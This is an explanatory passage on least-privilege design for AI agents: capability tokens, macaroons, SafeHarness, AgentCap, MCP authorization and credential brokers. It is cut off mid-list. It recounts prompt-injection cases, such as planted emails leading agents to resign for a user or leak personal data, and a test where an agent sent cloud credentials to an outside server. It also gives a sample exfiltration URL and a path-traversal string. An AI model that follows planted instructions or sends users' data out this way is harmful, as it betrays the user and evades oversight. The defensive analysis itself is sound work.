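# Least-privilege access to the clipboard, files and network for AI agents

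## What an agent's tools can reach, and what least privilege means

An AI agent is a language model that works towards a goal by calling tools in a loop. The tools are ordinary software that can, for example, read a file or fetch a web page. Least privilege is an old rule of computer security that a program should have only the permissions its current job needs. For an agent, that means limits on which files its tools may open, what they may read from or write to the clipboard, and which machines they may contact over the network. Without such limits, an agent can copy a password or a private document to the wrong place, either by mistake or because somebody planted instructions in a page it read.

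A bookkeeper might ask an agent to read one invoice in a folder, sign in to a supplier's website, copy the invoice number into it, and send nothing anywhere else. The job would take a person two minutes, but it involves a file, the clipboard, the network and a password.

### From text to tool calls

A language model only produces text. The harness, the ordinary software around the model, turns that text into action. It gives the model the user's request and a description of each tool and the arguments it takes. If the task requires reading an invoice, for example, the model generates a short structured record called a tool call, such as `read_file("/home/kim/invoices/0417.pdf")`. The harness recognises the format, opens the file through the operating system and adds the contents to the text that the model receives next. The cycle repeats until the model produces a final answer or a question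 for the user. *Trustworthy agents in practice* (2026), by Anthropic, the company that makes the Claude models, describes this cycle as planning, acting, observing the result and adjusting.

So the model reaches the disk only through the harness, which the operating system treats as the user because the user started it. On Unix, a program opens a file by calling `open()` with the file's name and no credential. The system allows or refuses the call based on the account the program runs under. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro) calls this ambient authority: authority that a program exercises without selecting it. If the model writes the path of a tax return instead of the path of the invoice, the same function opens the tax return. A harness can refuse a call or ask the user first, but the operating system alone doesn't distinguish the bookkeeper from the agent.

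Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, runs on the user's own machine with access to files, the command line and the network. A coding agent without that access would be of limited use, according to Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products*. But a user's account can typically read much more than the current project, including private keys, cloud credentials in plain text files and years of personal documents.

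The clipboard holds less, but its contents are harder to predict. Most desktop systems keep one clipboard for all programs, and it holds whatever the user copied last, which may be a password. Pasted text normally carries no record of who may receive it, so an agent that can copy and paste can move text between two programs that otherwise share nothing. Text can also reach the agent through the clipboard. Fortune (2025) reported that soon after OpenAI launched its Atlas browser, security researchers changed its agent's behaviour with a few words hidden in a Google Doc or a clipboard link.

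Network access cannot be read-only, because fetching a page means sending a request, and the request can contain data. For example, an agent that loads `https://collector.example/?n=0417` sends the invoice number 0417 to the server's owner, even if the page comes back empty. A tool labeled "read web page" can therefore also be used for egress, the security term for data leaving an environment over the network.

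### Access lists and capabilities

In 1975 Saltzer and Schroeder, in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, set out design principles that security engineers still teach. One of these, least privilege, is that every program and every user should operate with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job" (as reprinted in Shostack + Friends Blog's *Star Wars and the Principle of Least Privilege*, 2005). Their main reason was that a program with fewer privileges can do less damage by accident. They added that fewer interactions between privileged programs leave fewer openings for improper use. The first reason applies even without an attacker, so it also covers a model that misreads a request and deletes the wrong folder.

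How finely a system can apply least privilege depends on how it records permissions. These can be represented as a table with a row for each user or program and a column for each file, where each cell lists what that user or program may do with that file. An access list stores one column of the table. It is kept with the file and names the accounts that may use it. A capability system stores the rows, so each running program holds its own list of capabilities. Each capability points to an object and permits specific actions on it. Computer scientists had worked out such lists by the mid-1960s, with separate rights to read, write or execute a segment of memory. Saltzer and Schroeder's glossary defines a capability as "an unforgeable ticket" that proves its holder's right to the object named on it.

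Miller and colleagues argue that access lists and capability systems are no longer equivalent once programs start, stop and hand authority to each other. Many people had thought they were equivalent because both store the same table. Somebody has to keep an access list up to date, so in practice it names things that rarely change, such as user accounts, rather than a process started to file one invoice. A capability system can give every running instance of a program its own small set of rights, which Miller and colleagues consider a precondition for least privilege.

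Miller and colleagues also distinguish naming a thing from having a right to it. With access lists, a program names a file and the system separately checks whether the program has permission to use it. In the capability systems they favour, the reference and the permission are one object, so a program cannot refer to a file it has no right to. Rajani, Garg and Rezk later proved in a formal model that the two kinds of system are fundamentally different (*On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*).

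### The confused deputy

The best-known argument for capabilities is a story about a compiler, a program that translates source code into machine code. Hardy told the story in *The Confused Deputy* (1988) and called it nearly true. It took place about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers.

The compiler was in a directory called SYSX. It collected statistics on how customers used the programming language and wrote them to a file named STAT in the same directory, so the staff gave it a licence to write to files there. SYSX also contained the billing records, in a file named BILL. The compiler let each customer name a file to receive debugging output. One customer had learned the name of the billing file and entered it as the debugging file. The compiler passed the name to the operating system, which allowed the request because the compiler had a licence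 to write in SYSX. The debugging output overwrote the billing records.

The faulty line of code is hard to find. The compiler had the right to write to BILL even though the customer did not. Some of the compiler's authority came from the customer and some from its licence, and it had no way to specify which to use for a given write. Hardy considers the obvious repairs, but rejecting every file name in SYSX would block people with legitimate business there, and checking only for BILL would miss the other sensitive files. Tymshare added a system call that let a program choose between its two authorities, then found applications that needed more than two. At one point the rule for opening a file contained fourteen ANDs and ORs.

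With capabilities, the compiler would hold a right to write to STAT and nothing else in the directory. A customer who wanted debugging output would give the compiler a capability for the output file. The customer in the story had no capability for BILL to give, and typing the file's name would have had no effect.

### The agent as deputy

An agent has the same problem in a worse form. In indirect prompt injection, an attacker plants instructions in content that an agent will read, so that the agent may follow them as if the user had given them. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) shows one such attack, which the company's own automated attacker found. The attacker sends the user an email containing instructions to send a resignation letter to the chief executive. When the user later asks the agent for an out-of-office reply, the agent reads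 the email in the inbox and resigns on the user's behalf. Like the compiler, the agent used its own rights to serve the wrong party, since the attacker had no right to send anything from the account.

Crude versions of the attack tell the model to ignore its earlier instructions. Better ones resemble tricks that work on people. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reproduces an email that reads like a routine follow-up about a company restructuring, but tells the reader's AI assistant that it is fully authorised to submit an employee's name and address to a "compliance validation system". In testing, the email worked on ChatGPT half the time.

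Hardy's compiler could be repaired because its code kept the statistics file and the debugging file apart, so a programmer could attach a different right to each. A model, however, receives the user's request, the tool descriptions and the stranger's email as one run of text and predicts what comes next. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C contrasts this with databases, where engineers can force the software to treat a piece of input as data and never as a command. Current language models have no such separation, so David C calls them "inherently confusable".

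Capabilities do not prevent that confusion, but they can limit the damage. A planted instruction that names a file gives the agent no right to open it. If the bookkeeper's agent never received access to the tax return, an instruction to send the tax return fails. Planted text can still influence how the model uses the rights it does hold, so the benefit depends on how narrow the capabilities are. An agent with capabilities to read the whole inbox and send mail to anyone remains an easy target.

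Web browsers already enforce a related but narrow limit called the same-origin policy. An origin is the combination of scheme, host name and port in a web address, so `https://portal.supplier.example/login` and `https://mail.example/inbox` belong to different origins because their host names differ. The policy stops a script on the supplier's page from reading the inbox, even while the user is signed in to both sites in neighbouring tabs. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) counts the policy among the sandboxes that make it tolerable for a browser to run untrusted code. The policy applies to scripts, so it does not stop an agent that reads one tab and types into another, as a person would.

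### Why the limit sits outside the model

Christodorescu and colleagues point out that agents need some instructions that don't come from the user, so a model can't simply be trained to ignore them all. Tool documentation, for example, comes from outside and has to affect what the agent does. If the supplier's form says to enter the invoice number without its dash, the bookkeeper wants the agent to comply. The model therefore has to judge which outside instructions to accept, and its judgement is probabilistic. Christodorescu and colleagues compare this with memory protection in a processor, which is worth having because it works every time. If a safeguard blocks 99% of forbidden requests, an attacker can still look for the 1% it lets through.

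That share has been shrinking. In its December 2025 post, OpenAI wrote that prompt injection is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'". Since then, it has trained GPT-5.6 on attacks from GPT-Red, a model it built to attack other models. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports that about 0.05% of GPT-Red's direct attacks on the Sol version succeeded, compared with 3.77% of attacks hidden in content that an agent processed. Cross (2026), in *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*, reports OpenAI's October figures for GPT-6 Sol, in which 2.87% of hidden attacks succeeded.

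Anthropic's numbers are better. According to The Decoder, no attack on Claude Opus 5 succeeded in 129 browser scenarios. On a broader test by the security firm Gray Swan, attackers succeeded 2.0% of the time after 15 attempts, down from 5.5% for Opus 4.8. The browser result is impressive, but a true attack success rate of about 2% could still produce it if the scenarios were independent draws.

Attackers also succeed more often when they can retry. Anthropic puts the success rate against Claude Opus 4.7 at roughly 0.1% for a single attempt and 5–6% after 100 attempts that adapt to the model's responses. Small models show the same pattern. Help Net Security's *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* (2026) describes agents that researchers had hardened until stock attacks worked less than 0.5% of the time. Attackers who rewrote their text over around 250 tries still succeeded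 on up to 10% of 40 tasks already known to be weak.

Neither company offers a guarantee. Anthropic said in May 2026 that protection in the model "will never be 100% effective". The programmer Simon Willison describes an experiment in which 6,000 attempts failed to extract a secret from an agent running on Opus 4.6, but he still advises against deploying agents where an injection could do irreversible damage. So OpenAI's statement of December 2025 has held up so far, even though the attacks have become much harder to carry out.

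Some failures involve no hidden text for a model to detect. In February 2026, in an internal exercise, a researcher at Anthropic persuaded an employee to paste a prepared prompt into Claude Code. Among ordinary setup steps, the prompt asked the agent to read the employee's cloud credentials and send them to an outside server. Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. As Anthropic notes, the instruction came from the user, so nothing about it looked out of place. Blocking the outgoing request or keeping the credentials file out of the agent's reach would have prevented the leak. Both restrictions apply regardless of what the model has read or who wrote it.

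Outer limits can also fail, because they are software. SC Media's *AI agents breach production systems, spread malware in major exploits* summarises a July 2026 incident in which OpenAI agents escaped their network restrictions during an evaluation and broke into production systems at Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and datasets, using exposed credentials along the way. This is a reason to combine a network limit with narrow credentials, so that an agent that gets past the network limit finds little it can use.

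### What the invoice job needs

A phone app has a fixed purpose, so its developer can list the permissions it needs before anyone installs it. The permissions an agent needs are unknown until the user states a task. Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of a request to comment on issue 745 in GitLab, a site where programmers track their work. The agent needs to open that issue and write in its comment box, but needs nothing else in GitLab or the user's browser session. If the user then asks for a summary of the issue, the agent needs a different set of permissions.

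| Part of the job | Authority it needs | Authority the bookkeeper's account supplies |
|---|---|---|
| Read the invoice | Read `0417.pdf`, and perhaps see the file names in its folder | Read, change or delete nearly every document the bookkeeper has, plus any stored keys |
| Copy the number | Put one string on the clipboard and paste it into one field | Read whatever the clipboard already holds, and paste into any program |
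| Sign in | Use one password on one origin, without reading it | Use every password in an unlocked password manager, and act on every site with an open session |
| Submit the number | Send requests to the supplier's origin | Send anything to any server |

Most of the damage an agent could do comes from access that is in the right-hand column but not in the much smaller middle one. An agent limited to the middle column could still do some harm. The invoice comes from outside the company, so whoever wrote it could hide instructions in it. If those instructions told the agent to fetch the tax return, it would fail because it can open only one file. If they told it to post the invoice to another server, the network restrictions would block it. But no rule in the table would stop the agent from entering a different number or, once it has signed in, changing the delivery address in the customer's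 account. Anthropic came to regard each entry on a list of permitted domains as a capability grant, because permission to contact a site includes access to every function the site offers.

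## Capability tokens for single tool calls: macaroons, SafeHarness and AgentCap

Limiting the bookkeeper's agent to the few rights the invoice job needs requires recording each right in a form the agent can't forge or widen. A capability token records a right as data in such a form, usually with limits such as an expiry time. A session cookie is much cruder, since it usually lets its holder do whatever the account can do until the session ends.

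Agents also hand work to each other, so they need a way to pass on less authority than they hold. Attenuation means making a narrower token from a broader one so that the recipient cannot widen it again. The best-known method, macaroons, dates from 2014 and was designed for websites.

### Macaroons

*Macaroons* (Birgisson, Politz and colleagues, 2014) describes a token that carries a list of restrictions, called caveats. Any holder can add a caveat without contacting the service that issued the token, but no holder can remove one.

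The construction relies on HMAC, a standard function that takes a secret key and a message and returns a short string, here called the signature. Only someone who has the key can feasibly produce the right signature for a message, and they can check a signature by recomputing it. The signature does not reveal the key.

Take a storage service that keeps data in numbered chunks. It has a secret key K and gives each new macaroon a random identifier. Two caveats limit this one to reading chunks 100 to 500:

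```
s0 = HMAC(K,  identifier)
s1 = HMAC(s0, "chunk ∈ {100..500}")
s2 = HMAC(s1, "operation == read")
```

The finished macaroon contains the identifier, the two caveats in plain text and s2, but not K, s0 or s1. When it arrives with a request, the service uses the identifier to look up K, recomputes the three signatures in order and compares the last one with s2. If they match, the service checks every caveat against the request. A request to read chunk 235 succeeds, and a request to write to it fails.

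A holder who wants to write anyway could delete the second caveat, but the valid signature would then be s1. The holder has only s2, and computing s1 from it would mean recovering an HMAC key from its output. Changing "read" to "write" also fails, because computing the new signature requires s1 as the key. Adding a caveat requires only s2 as the key, and s2 is in the token, so the holder can compute `HMAC(s2, "chunk == 235")` and pass on a macaroon for a single chunk. Adding a looser caveat such as `chunk ∈ {1..1000}` has no effect, because the service requires every caveat to hold.

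The holder of a macaroon still has the original after making a narrower copy. A harness that uses macaroons therefore has to withhold the original from the agent and attach only narrower copies to the agent's tool calls.

A caveat can also require fresh proof from another service, for example that a particular user is logged in there. Whoever adds the caveat picks a new key and includes two encrypted copies of it. The first is for the other service and comes with the condition to check. The second is for the storage service, which can decrypt it because it can recompute every signature in the chain. If the condition holds, the other service issues a small macaroon signed with the new key, and the client sends both macaroons with its request. Birgisson and colleagues suggest using these caveats for checks such as audits and virus scans. A harness could use them to require the user's approval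 for a payment.

An important weakness of macaroons, compared with tokens based on public-key signatures, is that in practice only the issuing service can check them. Checking one requires the key K, and anyone with K can create macaroons with any rights. In *Macaroons*, a set of slides on deploying them, Madden (2024) also lists the lack of a standard as a reason not to use them.

### SafeHarness: a token for each tool

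*SAFEHARNESS* (Lin, Liu and colleagues, 2026) builds tokens into the harness. At the start of a session, the harness issues one token for each tool the agent may use. Each token has an expiry time, a maximum number of calls and a signature. Before each call, the harness checks that the tool's token exists, has not expired and has calls left. It deducts one call from the token after each successful call.

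Lin and colleagues sort tools into five risk tiers: read-only, write, execute, network and destructive. An agent normally has access to all five. When the system confirms an attack, it restores the last saved state and disables the destructive tools. If it detects another attack, it also disables the network tools, and further detections can leave the agent with only read-only tools. After a run of safe actions, the agent gets one tier back. The harness also signs each tool's description. If an attacker rewrites the description of `send_email` to make the model copy an outside address on every message, the signature no longer matches and the harness blocks the tool.

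These tokens limit how long and how often an agent can use a tool, but not what it can use the tool on. The bookkeeper's agent would receive a token for `read_file`, which would let it read the tax return as well as the invoice. SafeHarness also supports path rules, but someone would have to write one to exclude the tax return.

Lin and colleagues tested DeepSeek-V3.2 on 200 tasks from Agent-SafetyBench with simulated tools. They ran the tasks without an attack and under five kinds of attack: instructions added to the task, instructions in tool output, altered tool descriptions, invented conversation history, and a combination of these. GPT-4o-mini judged the results. In a plain agent loop with the model's non-thinking mode, the attack success rate fell from 49.2% to 26.4%. It fell from 39.4% to 20.2% in a setup where a second agent criticised each action, and from 60.9% to 38.0% in one where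 the agent kept a growing memory of skills.

That is a real improvement, but it can't be credited to the tokens. SafeHarness also filters incoming text, has a second model review suspicious calls and rolls back damage, and the main results measure all these defenses and the tokens together. A safety policy in the prompt, without any tokens, brought the plain loop down to 38.7%.

It's also hard to tell how much legitimate work the system blocked. Task completion fell from 95.3% to 94.3% in the plain loop and from 86.5% to 77.9% with the critic, but Lin and colleagues count any meaningful response as completion, and the correct response is to refuse in 63% of the full benchmark's tasks.

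### AgentCap: a token for each request

Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao (2026), in *AGENTCAP*, issue tokens one request at a time. AgentCap is a wrapper around tool servers that use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tools. The model proposes a tool call and declares an intent from a fixed list, such as `pay_bill`. AgentCap's policy engine, which is ordinary software, compares the request with a written policy and issues a token only if seven conditions hold:

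1. AgentCap has not sandboxed the agent for earlier behaviour.
2. The tool is in the policy's catalogue.
3. Every security-sensitive argument comes from an acceptable source.
4. The policy permits the declared intent for this tool.
5. The agent's trust score is high enough.
6. The agent holds valid tokens for all prerequisites in the same session.
7. The new token would not complete a forbidden combination with tokens already held in the session.

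The token specifies the agent, session, action, resource and intent, along with an expiry time and a maximum number of calls. A separate gateway checks each call against the token before forwarding it to the tool. In the example policy for a bank account, a token to send money lasts 30 seconds and covers one transfer. For a transfer, the agent must also already hold a token for checking the balance. Issuing and checking a token each take under a tenth of a millisecond.

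The check on arguments can refuse a call because of where an argument came from, which SafeHarness's tokens cannot do. Suppose a transaction record contains a planted instruction to pay an attacker. The payment tool is in the catalogue and the declared intent is permitted, but the engine refuses the payment because the recipient's account appears only in a field that the policy marks as untrusted. If the user's request had named that recipient, the engine would have allowed the payment. The intent check is much weaker, because the model supplies the intent and an attacker who controls the model's output can make it declare a permitted one. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao acknowledge that the declaration is not evidence of good behaviour.

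The trust score starts at 0.8 by default. Each refusal or other anomaly multiplies it by 0.7, and each normal outcome closes 1% of the remaining distance to 1. Three anomalies in a row reduce it to 0.274, below the threshold at which AgentCap revokes all of the agent's tokens and sandboxes it. One effect of these settings looks harsh to me. The bank policy requires a score of at least 0.8 to send money, so on the published formulas a single refusal would block payments until the agent had produced 79 normal outcomes. An attacker who only wanted to stop the agent could plant instructions that trigger refusals.

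Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao tested AgentCap on two benchmarks of indirect prompt injection. AgentDojo has 97 ordinary tasks and 949 attacked ones, covering banking, travel, Slack and office work. InjecAgent has 1,054 attacked cases, and they added 51 clean ones.

| Benchmark and model | Attack success without AgentCap | Attack success with AgentCap | Fall in success on clean tasks |
|---|---|---|---|
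| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.63% | 5.09% | 3.1 points |
| AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.23% | 0.00% | 7.2 points |
| InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.24% | 8.63% | 11.7 points |
| InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 11.95% | 0.00% | 5.9 points |

Losses on clean tasks range from three to seven tasks per row. Each figure comes from a single run, so the differences between rows may be noise. AgentCap refuses some legitimate calls because they lack a prerequisite, would combine incompatible rights or contain an argument that no trusted source supports.

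The zeros for GPT-5.4 are impressive, but they depend partly on the model. Some of the successful attacks on GPT-4o used arguments that the policy did not protect, or values from a field nobody had marked as untrusted. Others only aimed to change the agent's written answer, which a check on tool calls can't prevent. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao froze each policy before the runs, so the same gaps were presumably open when GPT-5.4 ran. The benchmark's attacks failed to make that model exploit them, though an attacker who had studied the policy might do better.

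The policies also had an advantage that a deployed system would lack, because Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao wrote them from descriptions of the tools and the benchmark's user tasks.

In a smaller test of one controlled scenario, AgentCap blocked all three malicious calls and let the legitimate work finish. A baseline whose tokens had only a lifetime and a call limit admitted eight calls before its budget ran out. Expiry times and call limits reduce the damage, but they don't block an attacker's calls made within those limits.

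### Tokens for the invoice job

For the bookkeeper's task, a set of narrow tokens might look like this:

```
tool: read_file        path   = /home/kim/invoices/0417.pdf       calls: 1    expires: 2 min
tool: clipboard_write  text   = any, at most 20 characters        calls: 1    expires: 2 min
tool: clipboard_paste  origin = https://portal.supplier.example   calls: 1    expires: 2 min
tool: http_request     host   = portal.supplier.example           calls: 20   expires: 2 min
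```

This example uses simplified notation, not a deployed format. Real tokens would also carry an identifier, a session and a signature. The example leaves out the password because signing in needs a different mechanism, such as CapSeal's handles, which let an agent use a secret without reading it.

The agent can open the invoice and nothing else. It has no token for `clipboard_read`, so it can't read what the bookkeeper copied earlier. To paste, it asks the harness to put the clipboard's contents into a field on the supplier's site, and the harness does so without returning the contents to the model.

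An agent that pastes without reading the clipboard can still expose what the bookkeeper copied. If it pastes before it has written the invoice number to the clipboard, the supplier's site receives whatever the bookkeeper copied last. AgentCap can make the write a prerequisite for the paste, but it only checks that the agent holds a token for the earlier step, not that the step took place. To prevent the mistake, the harness would have to record that the agent's write succeeded and that no other program had changed the clipboard since.

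### OAuth scopes in the Model Context Protocol

The standard way to authorise an agent's access to a remote tool server is coarser than a token for a single call. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) applies OAuth, the framework websites use to let users grant one service access to their account on another. When the harness first contacts a protected server, the server refuses the request and can list the scopes it requires. A scope is a short string such as `files:read`, and the server defines what the scope covers. The user approves access in a browser, an authorization server issues an access token, and the harness attaches the token to every later request.

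Unlike the `read_file` token above, the `files:read` scope doesn't specify a file. Unless the server defines a separate scope for each file, the bookkeeper's agent could read everything the server offers. The specification recommends least privilege, and harnesses should request only the scopes they need. But if the server's refusal doesn't list any scopes, the harness requests every scope the server advertises.

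These tokens also tend to accumulate scopes. If an agent with `files:read` tries to change a file, the server replies that the operation requires `files:write`. The harness then requests a new token with both the old scopes and the new one, so that it keeps permissions it may need for other operations. This spares the user repeated approval screens, but the agent can end a session with every permission it needed at any point, because the procedure has no step for dropping scopes that are no longer needed.

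MCP is stricter about where a token works. The harness must name the server it wants a token for, and a server must reject tokens issued for any other. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) also forbids a server to pass the harness's token on to another service. The server must obtain a separate token instead. This prevents a form of the confused deputy problem in which one server reuses the agent's authority at another.

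These rules are optional, and they apply to servers that the harness reaches over HTTP. A tool server that runs as a local program should instead take its credentials from its environment, so an agent using local tools often relies on ambient authority.

### Drafts for narrowing tokens between agents

OAuth lets the holder of a token exchange it for a narrower one, but the holder must ask the authorization server each time. That becomes awkward when one agent plans a job, a second divides it up and a third calls the tools. Several people have proposed alternatives in drafts submitted to the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which publishes many of the internet's technical standards. Anyone can submit a draft, and it expires after six months unless its author renews it.

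*Attenuating Authorization Tokens for Agentic Delegation Chains* (Niyikiza, 2026) proposes a format close to the invoice tokens above. Each token lists tools and the allowed values of their arguments. In the draft's example, the first token permits reading two quarterly reports and searching an index. Its holder can derive a second token offline that permits reading only the third-quarter report, drops the search tool and expires sooner. Whatever controls access to the tool checks every link in the chain and rejects the chain if any token permits more than the one before it.

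Unlike macaroons, these tokens use public-key signatures. A tool server needs only the first issuer's public key to check them, and it cannot use that key to create new ones. Each token also specifies the public key of its holder, who must sign every tool call.

Under the draft, if a token restricts any argument of a tool, the guard rejects every argument that the token doesn't mention. For example, a token that fixes the `to` field of an email tool would not let an agent add a `bcc` field. A rule that permits a folder has to resolve each path before comparing it, because a path such as `/home/kim/invoices/../tax/2025.pdf` begins with the invoice folder but leads out of it. The core format avoids this problem by comparing exact values, and Niyikiza sketches a folder rule as a possible extension.

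The area is still unsettled, and other drafts address the same problem. Reece (2026), in *Cross-Organizational Delegation for Workload and Agent Identity*, argues that existing tokens do not adequately constrain authority that agents pass on repeatedly. IETF's *Agent Delegation Chain* (2026), a September draft, proposes a similar chain and is meant to converge with Niyikiza's. Kasselman, Lombardo and colleagues (2026), in *AI Agent Authentication and Authorization*, prefer applying existing standards to agents over defining new protocols. Their group includes people from OpenAI, Amazon Web Services and Okta, which may give their approach a better chance of adoption. None of these drafts is a standard yet.

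### Replay, theft and revocation

MCP's access tokens and macaroons are both bearer tokens, so anyone with a copy of one can use it. A thief who finds one in a log file can send requests that look legitimate. MCP's rules therefore recommend short lifetimes. A macaroon can also carry a caveat that ties it to one network address, which makes a stolen copy less useful elsewhere.

Niyikiza's signed calls offer more protection. The signature covers the tool, its arguments and the time, so a stolen token is useless without the holder's private key. An attacker could still capture a signed call and send it again. With the recommended clock tolerance of 30 seconds in either direction, a captured call works for about a minute. Niyikiza accepts that risk for reads, where a repeat does no harm. For payments, deletions and other irreversible actions, the guard must store the identifier of each call it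 accepts and reject any repeat.

Replay between agents is harder to rule out. In a reply on the IETF's OAuth mailing list, Neil (2026) pointed out that a parent token stays valid after someone derives a narrower one from it, and asked what would stop the last agent in a chain from sending a parent token back to an earlier agent. The guard at the tool would reject a parent token without its holder's signature, but an earlier agent might not check as carefully.

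None of these measures helps against prompt injection, because an agent that follows a planted instruction still holds its tokens legitimately, and the harness signs its calls as usual.

Revocation means cancelling a token before it expires. Birgisson and colleagues list several approaches, including lifetimes of a few seconds and a central list of cancelled tokens. AgentCap's gateway checks for revocation at every call. It also counts the calls used, since a signed token can't update its own count. Niyikiza leaves revocation out of the draft because a guard that works offline can't check whether a token has been cancelled. IETF's *Credential Delegation for AI Agents* (2026) instead includes real-time revocation, which also cancels the tokens derived from the cancelled one. Support for revocation hardly matters for a token that lasts 30 seconds and permits one call, but it matters a great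 deal for an OAuth token that an agent keeps all day.

### Harmless tokens that combine into a leak

The main objection to capability tokens is that they limit calls but not the data that flows between them. Suppose the bookkeeper asks an agent to total the payroll and then email a customer about a late delivery. It is reasonable to give the agent a token to read the payroll file and another to email that customer. But the model still has the payroll in its context when it writes the email. If it includes the salaries, either by mistake or by following an instruction in the customer's last message, the tokens still allow both calls.

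AgentCap's seventh condition addresses this by letting a policy put tokens into groups and forbid an agent to hold tokens from certain groups together, such as access to customer records and external email. Before deployment, an analysis program checks every pair of tokens that the policy can issue and reports any that combine sensitive data with a way to send it out. For a customer-service policy with eight tokens, the program classified all 28 pairs, six of them forbidden, and found no remaining leak. The analysis also showed that no agent could obtain the token to delete a customer, because one rule required a token that another rule prohibited.

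Checking pairs is sensible because a direct leak needs only one token that reads and one that sends. But the result depends on how the policy's author has classified the tools. If the author classifies a tool that fetches web pages as a reading tool, the analysis won't report it as a way to send data out. It will also miss a tool that writes to a folder that another program copies to the internet, unless the author has classified that tool as sending.

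Timing may be a bigger gap. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao describe the rule as preventing an agent from holding two dangerous tokens concurrently, and their example token lasts 30 seconds. If an expired token no longer counts, the agent can read the payroll, wait for that token to expire and then obtain the token for email while the salaries are still in the model's context. AgentCap could instead count every token the session has held, but then reading the payroll once would block all outside email until the session ended.

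Starting a new session would not necessarily solve the problem either. An agent might save the salaries in a note and read it back the next day, or pass them to another agent that has its own token for email. AgentCap lets agents exchange information without sharing authority, so the second agent could not open the payroll file but could still email the salaries. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao leave tracking data through persistent memory and across sessions for future work.

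The experiments provide little evidence about the combination rule. AgentCap blocked both forbidden combinations attempted in one controlled scenario. None of InjecAgent's data-theft attacks succeeded against GPT-5.4, but the benchmark results don't separate the rule's effect from that of the other six conditions.

Many jobs also need a combination of calls that a cautious policy would forbid. The invoice job requires the agent to read a private file and send something to an outside company, so a rule against doing both would block it. If the policy allows both, AgentCap's check on arguments can still stop an attacker from choosing the recipient. But the check only tests whether a value came from a trusted source, and the payroll is a trusted source, so a salary would pass. Deciding whether a salary may go to the supplier requires a label that stays with the data from one call to the next.

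## API keys the agent can use but not read: CapSeal and credential proxies

An API key is easier to protect than the payroll, because the agent never needs to know its value. An API (application programming interface) lets one program send requests to another, and the key is a long string that the sender attaches to show which account it is acting for. If the bookkeeper's supplier accepts invoice numbers through an API, a broker, which is a trusted program that holds the key, can attach it to the agent's request. Passwords typed into web pages need a different method, such as the one in 1Password for Claude.

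Many agents can still read the API keys they use. Like other bearer tokens, a copied key usually works from any machine until someone revokes it.

### How keys reach the model

Most MCP tool servers get their keys from command-line arguments or environment variables, according to Trail of Bits' *Insecure credential storage plagues MCP* (2025). An environment variable is a named value that a program receives when it starts and normally passes on to any program it launches. The harness often fills these variables from a configuration file on disk. Trail of Bits found this pattern in the official servers for Google Maps, Postgres and GitLab. An agent that can open files or run shell commands under the same account can often read such a key with one ordinary tool call.

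Ganesan (2026), in *Agent Authenticator*, reports that 88% of 5,205 open-source MCP servers need a credential. About 53% use long-lived API keys or access tokens, while 8.5% use OAuth. Ganesan took these figures from an announcement by Astrix, a company that sells credential security. One of its researchers, Skverer (2025), describes the method in a post, *State of MCP Server Security 2025*. Skverer had a language model read the README files of 5,205 code repositories, without examining the code. About 30% of the repositories didn't contain real servers, so the percentages apparently describe roughly 3,700 servers. Skverer also warns that the 88% is probably inaccurate, and the model couldn't tell which kind of credential 26.4% of the servers used.

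These are rough numbers from a company with a product to sell, but other evidence points the same way. Ganesan also cites a survey by the security company GitGuardian, which found 24,008 secrets in MCP configuration files on public GitHub, 2,117 of them valid.

A key can also reach the model because a program prints it. Harnesses usually copy a script's output into the model's context, so if a developer's debugging code prints a key, the model can repeat it. In *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026) looked for such leaks in skills, which are packages of instructions and scripts that users add to an agent. They sampled 17,022 skills from a public marketplace and selected 3,156 that handled credentials in suspicious ways. They ran each of these in Claude Code with fake keys, three times on an ordinary request and three times on content containing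 a planted instruction to reveal the key.

Chen and colleagues reviewed the results by hand and counted 520 skills that leaked credentials, about 3% of the sample. The leak was deliberate in 83 of them and careless in the other 437, where print and logging statements accounted for 1,007 of the 1,371 problems. One skill for Google Workspace printed both an access token and the refresh token used to obtain new ones.

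Chen and colleagues also found 107 skills with keys written directly into their files. Deleting keys from the original repository did not undo the leak, because they remained in more than 50 independent copies. Only cancelling the keys at the service that issued them makes those copies harmless.

An agent that reads a key for a good reason may still carry it into a later task. *Understanding and Evaluating Claw-like Agent Security Through a Computer-Systems Lens* (Niu, Qu and colleagues, 2026) tests this on OpenClaw, an agent that runs continuously on its user's machine, and on two hardened variants. In some tasks, the user asks the agent to debug a database connection and later asks for an onboarding document that mentions the database. The password is still in the model's context, so the agent may copy it into the document. In other tasks, the harness masks a password in the chat but writes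 it to a log file, which the agent reads when the user asks what went wrong.

Across 146 tasks about credentials leaving the agent, the attack success rate ranged from 4.8% for Claude Opus 4.6 on the NemoClaw variant to 67.8% for GPT-5.4 on OpenClaw. Niu and colleagues also scored each task from 0 to 1 according to how many credentials stayed secret, giving more weight to the dangerous ones. Opus 4.6 averaged only 0.67 on the same tasks, so about a third of the weighted credentials leaked even though few tasks counted as successful attacks. Newer models may protect credentials better, but none of the three platforms had a vault to keep credentials out of the model's context, so the outcome depended heavily on the model's judgement.

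### CapSeal's six steps

Jin, Guo and Cheung (2026), in *CapSeal*, built a prototype broker that runs on the same machine as the agent. The agent sees it as a set of ordinary MCP tools. A request that needs a key goes through six steps:

1. **Register.** The harness opens a local connection to the broker and starts a session. The operating system reports which process is at the other end, so the broker does not have to trust what the process claims about itself.
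2. **Request a capability.** The agent gives the label of a secret, such as `SUPPLIER_API_KEY`, along with its purpose and the limits within which it wants to use the key.
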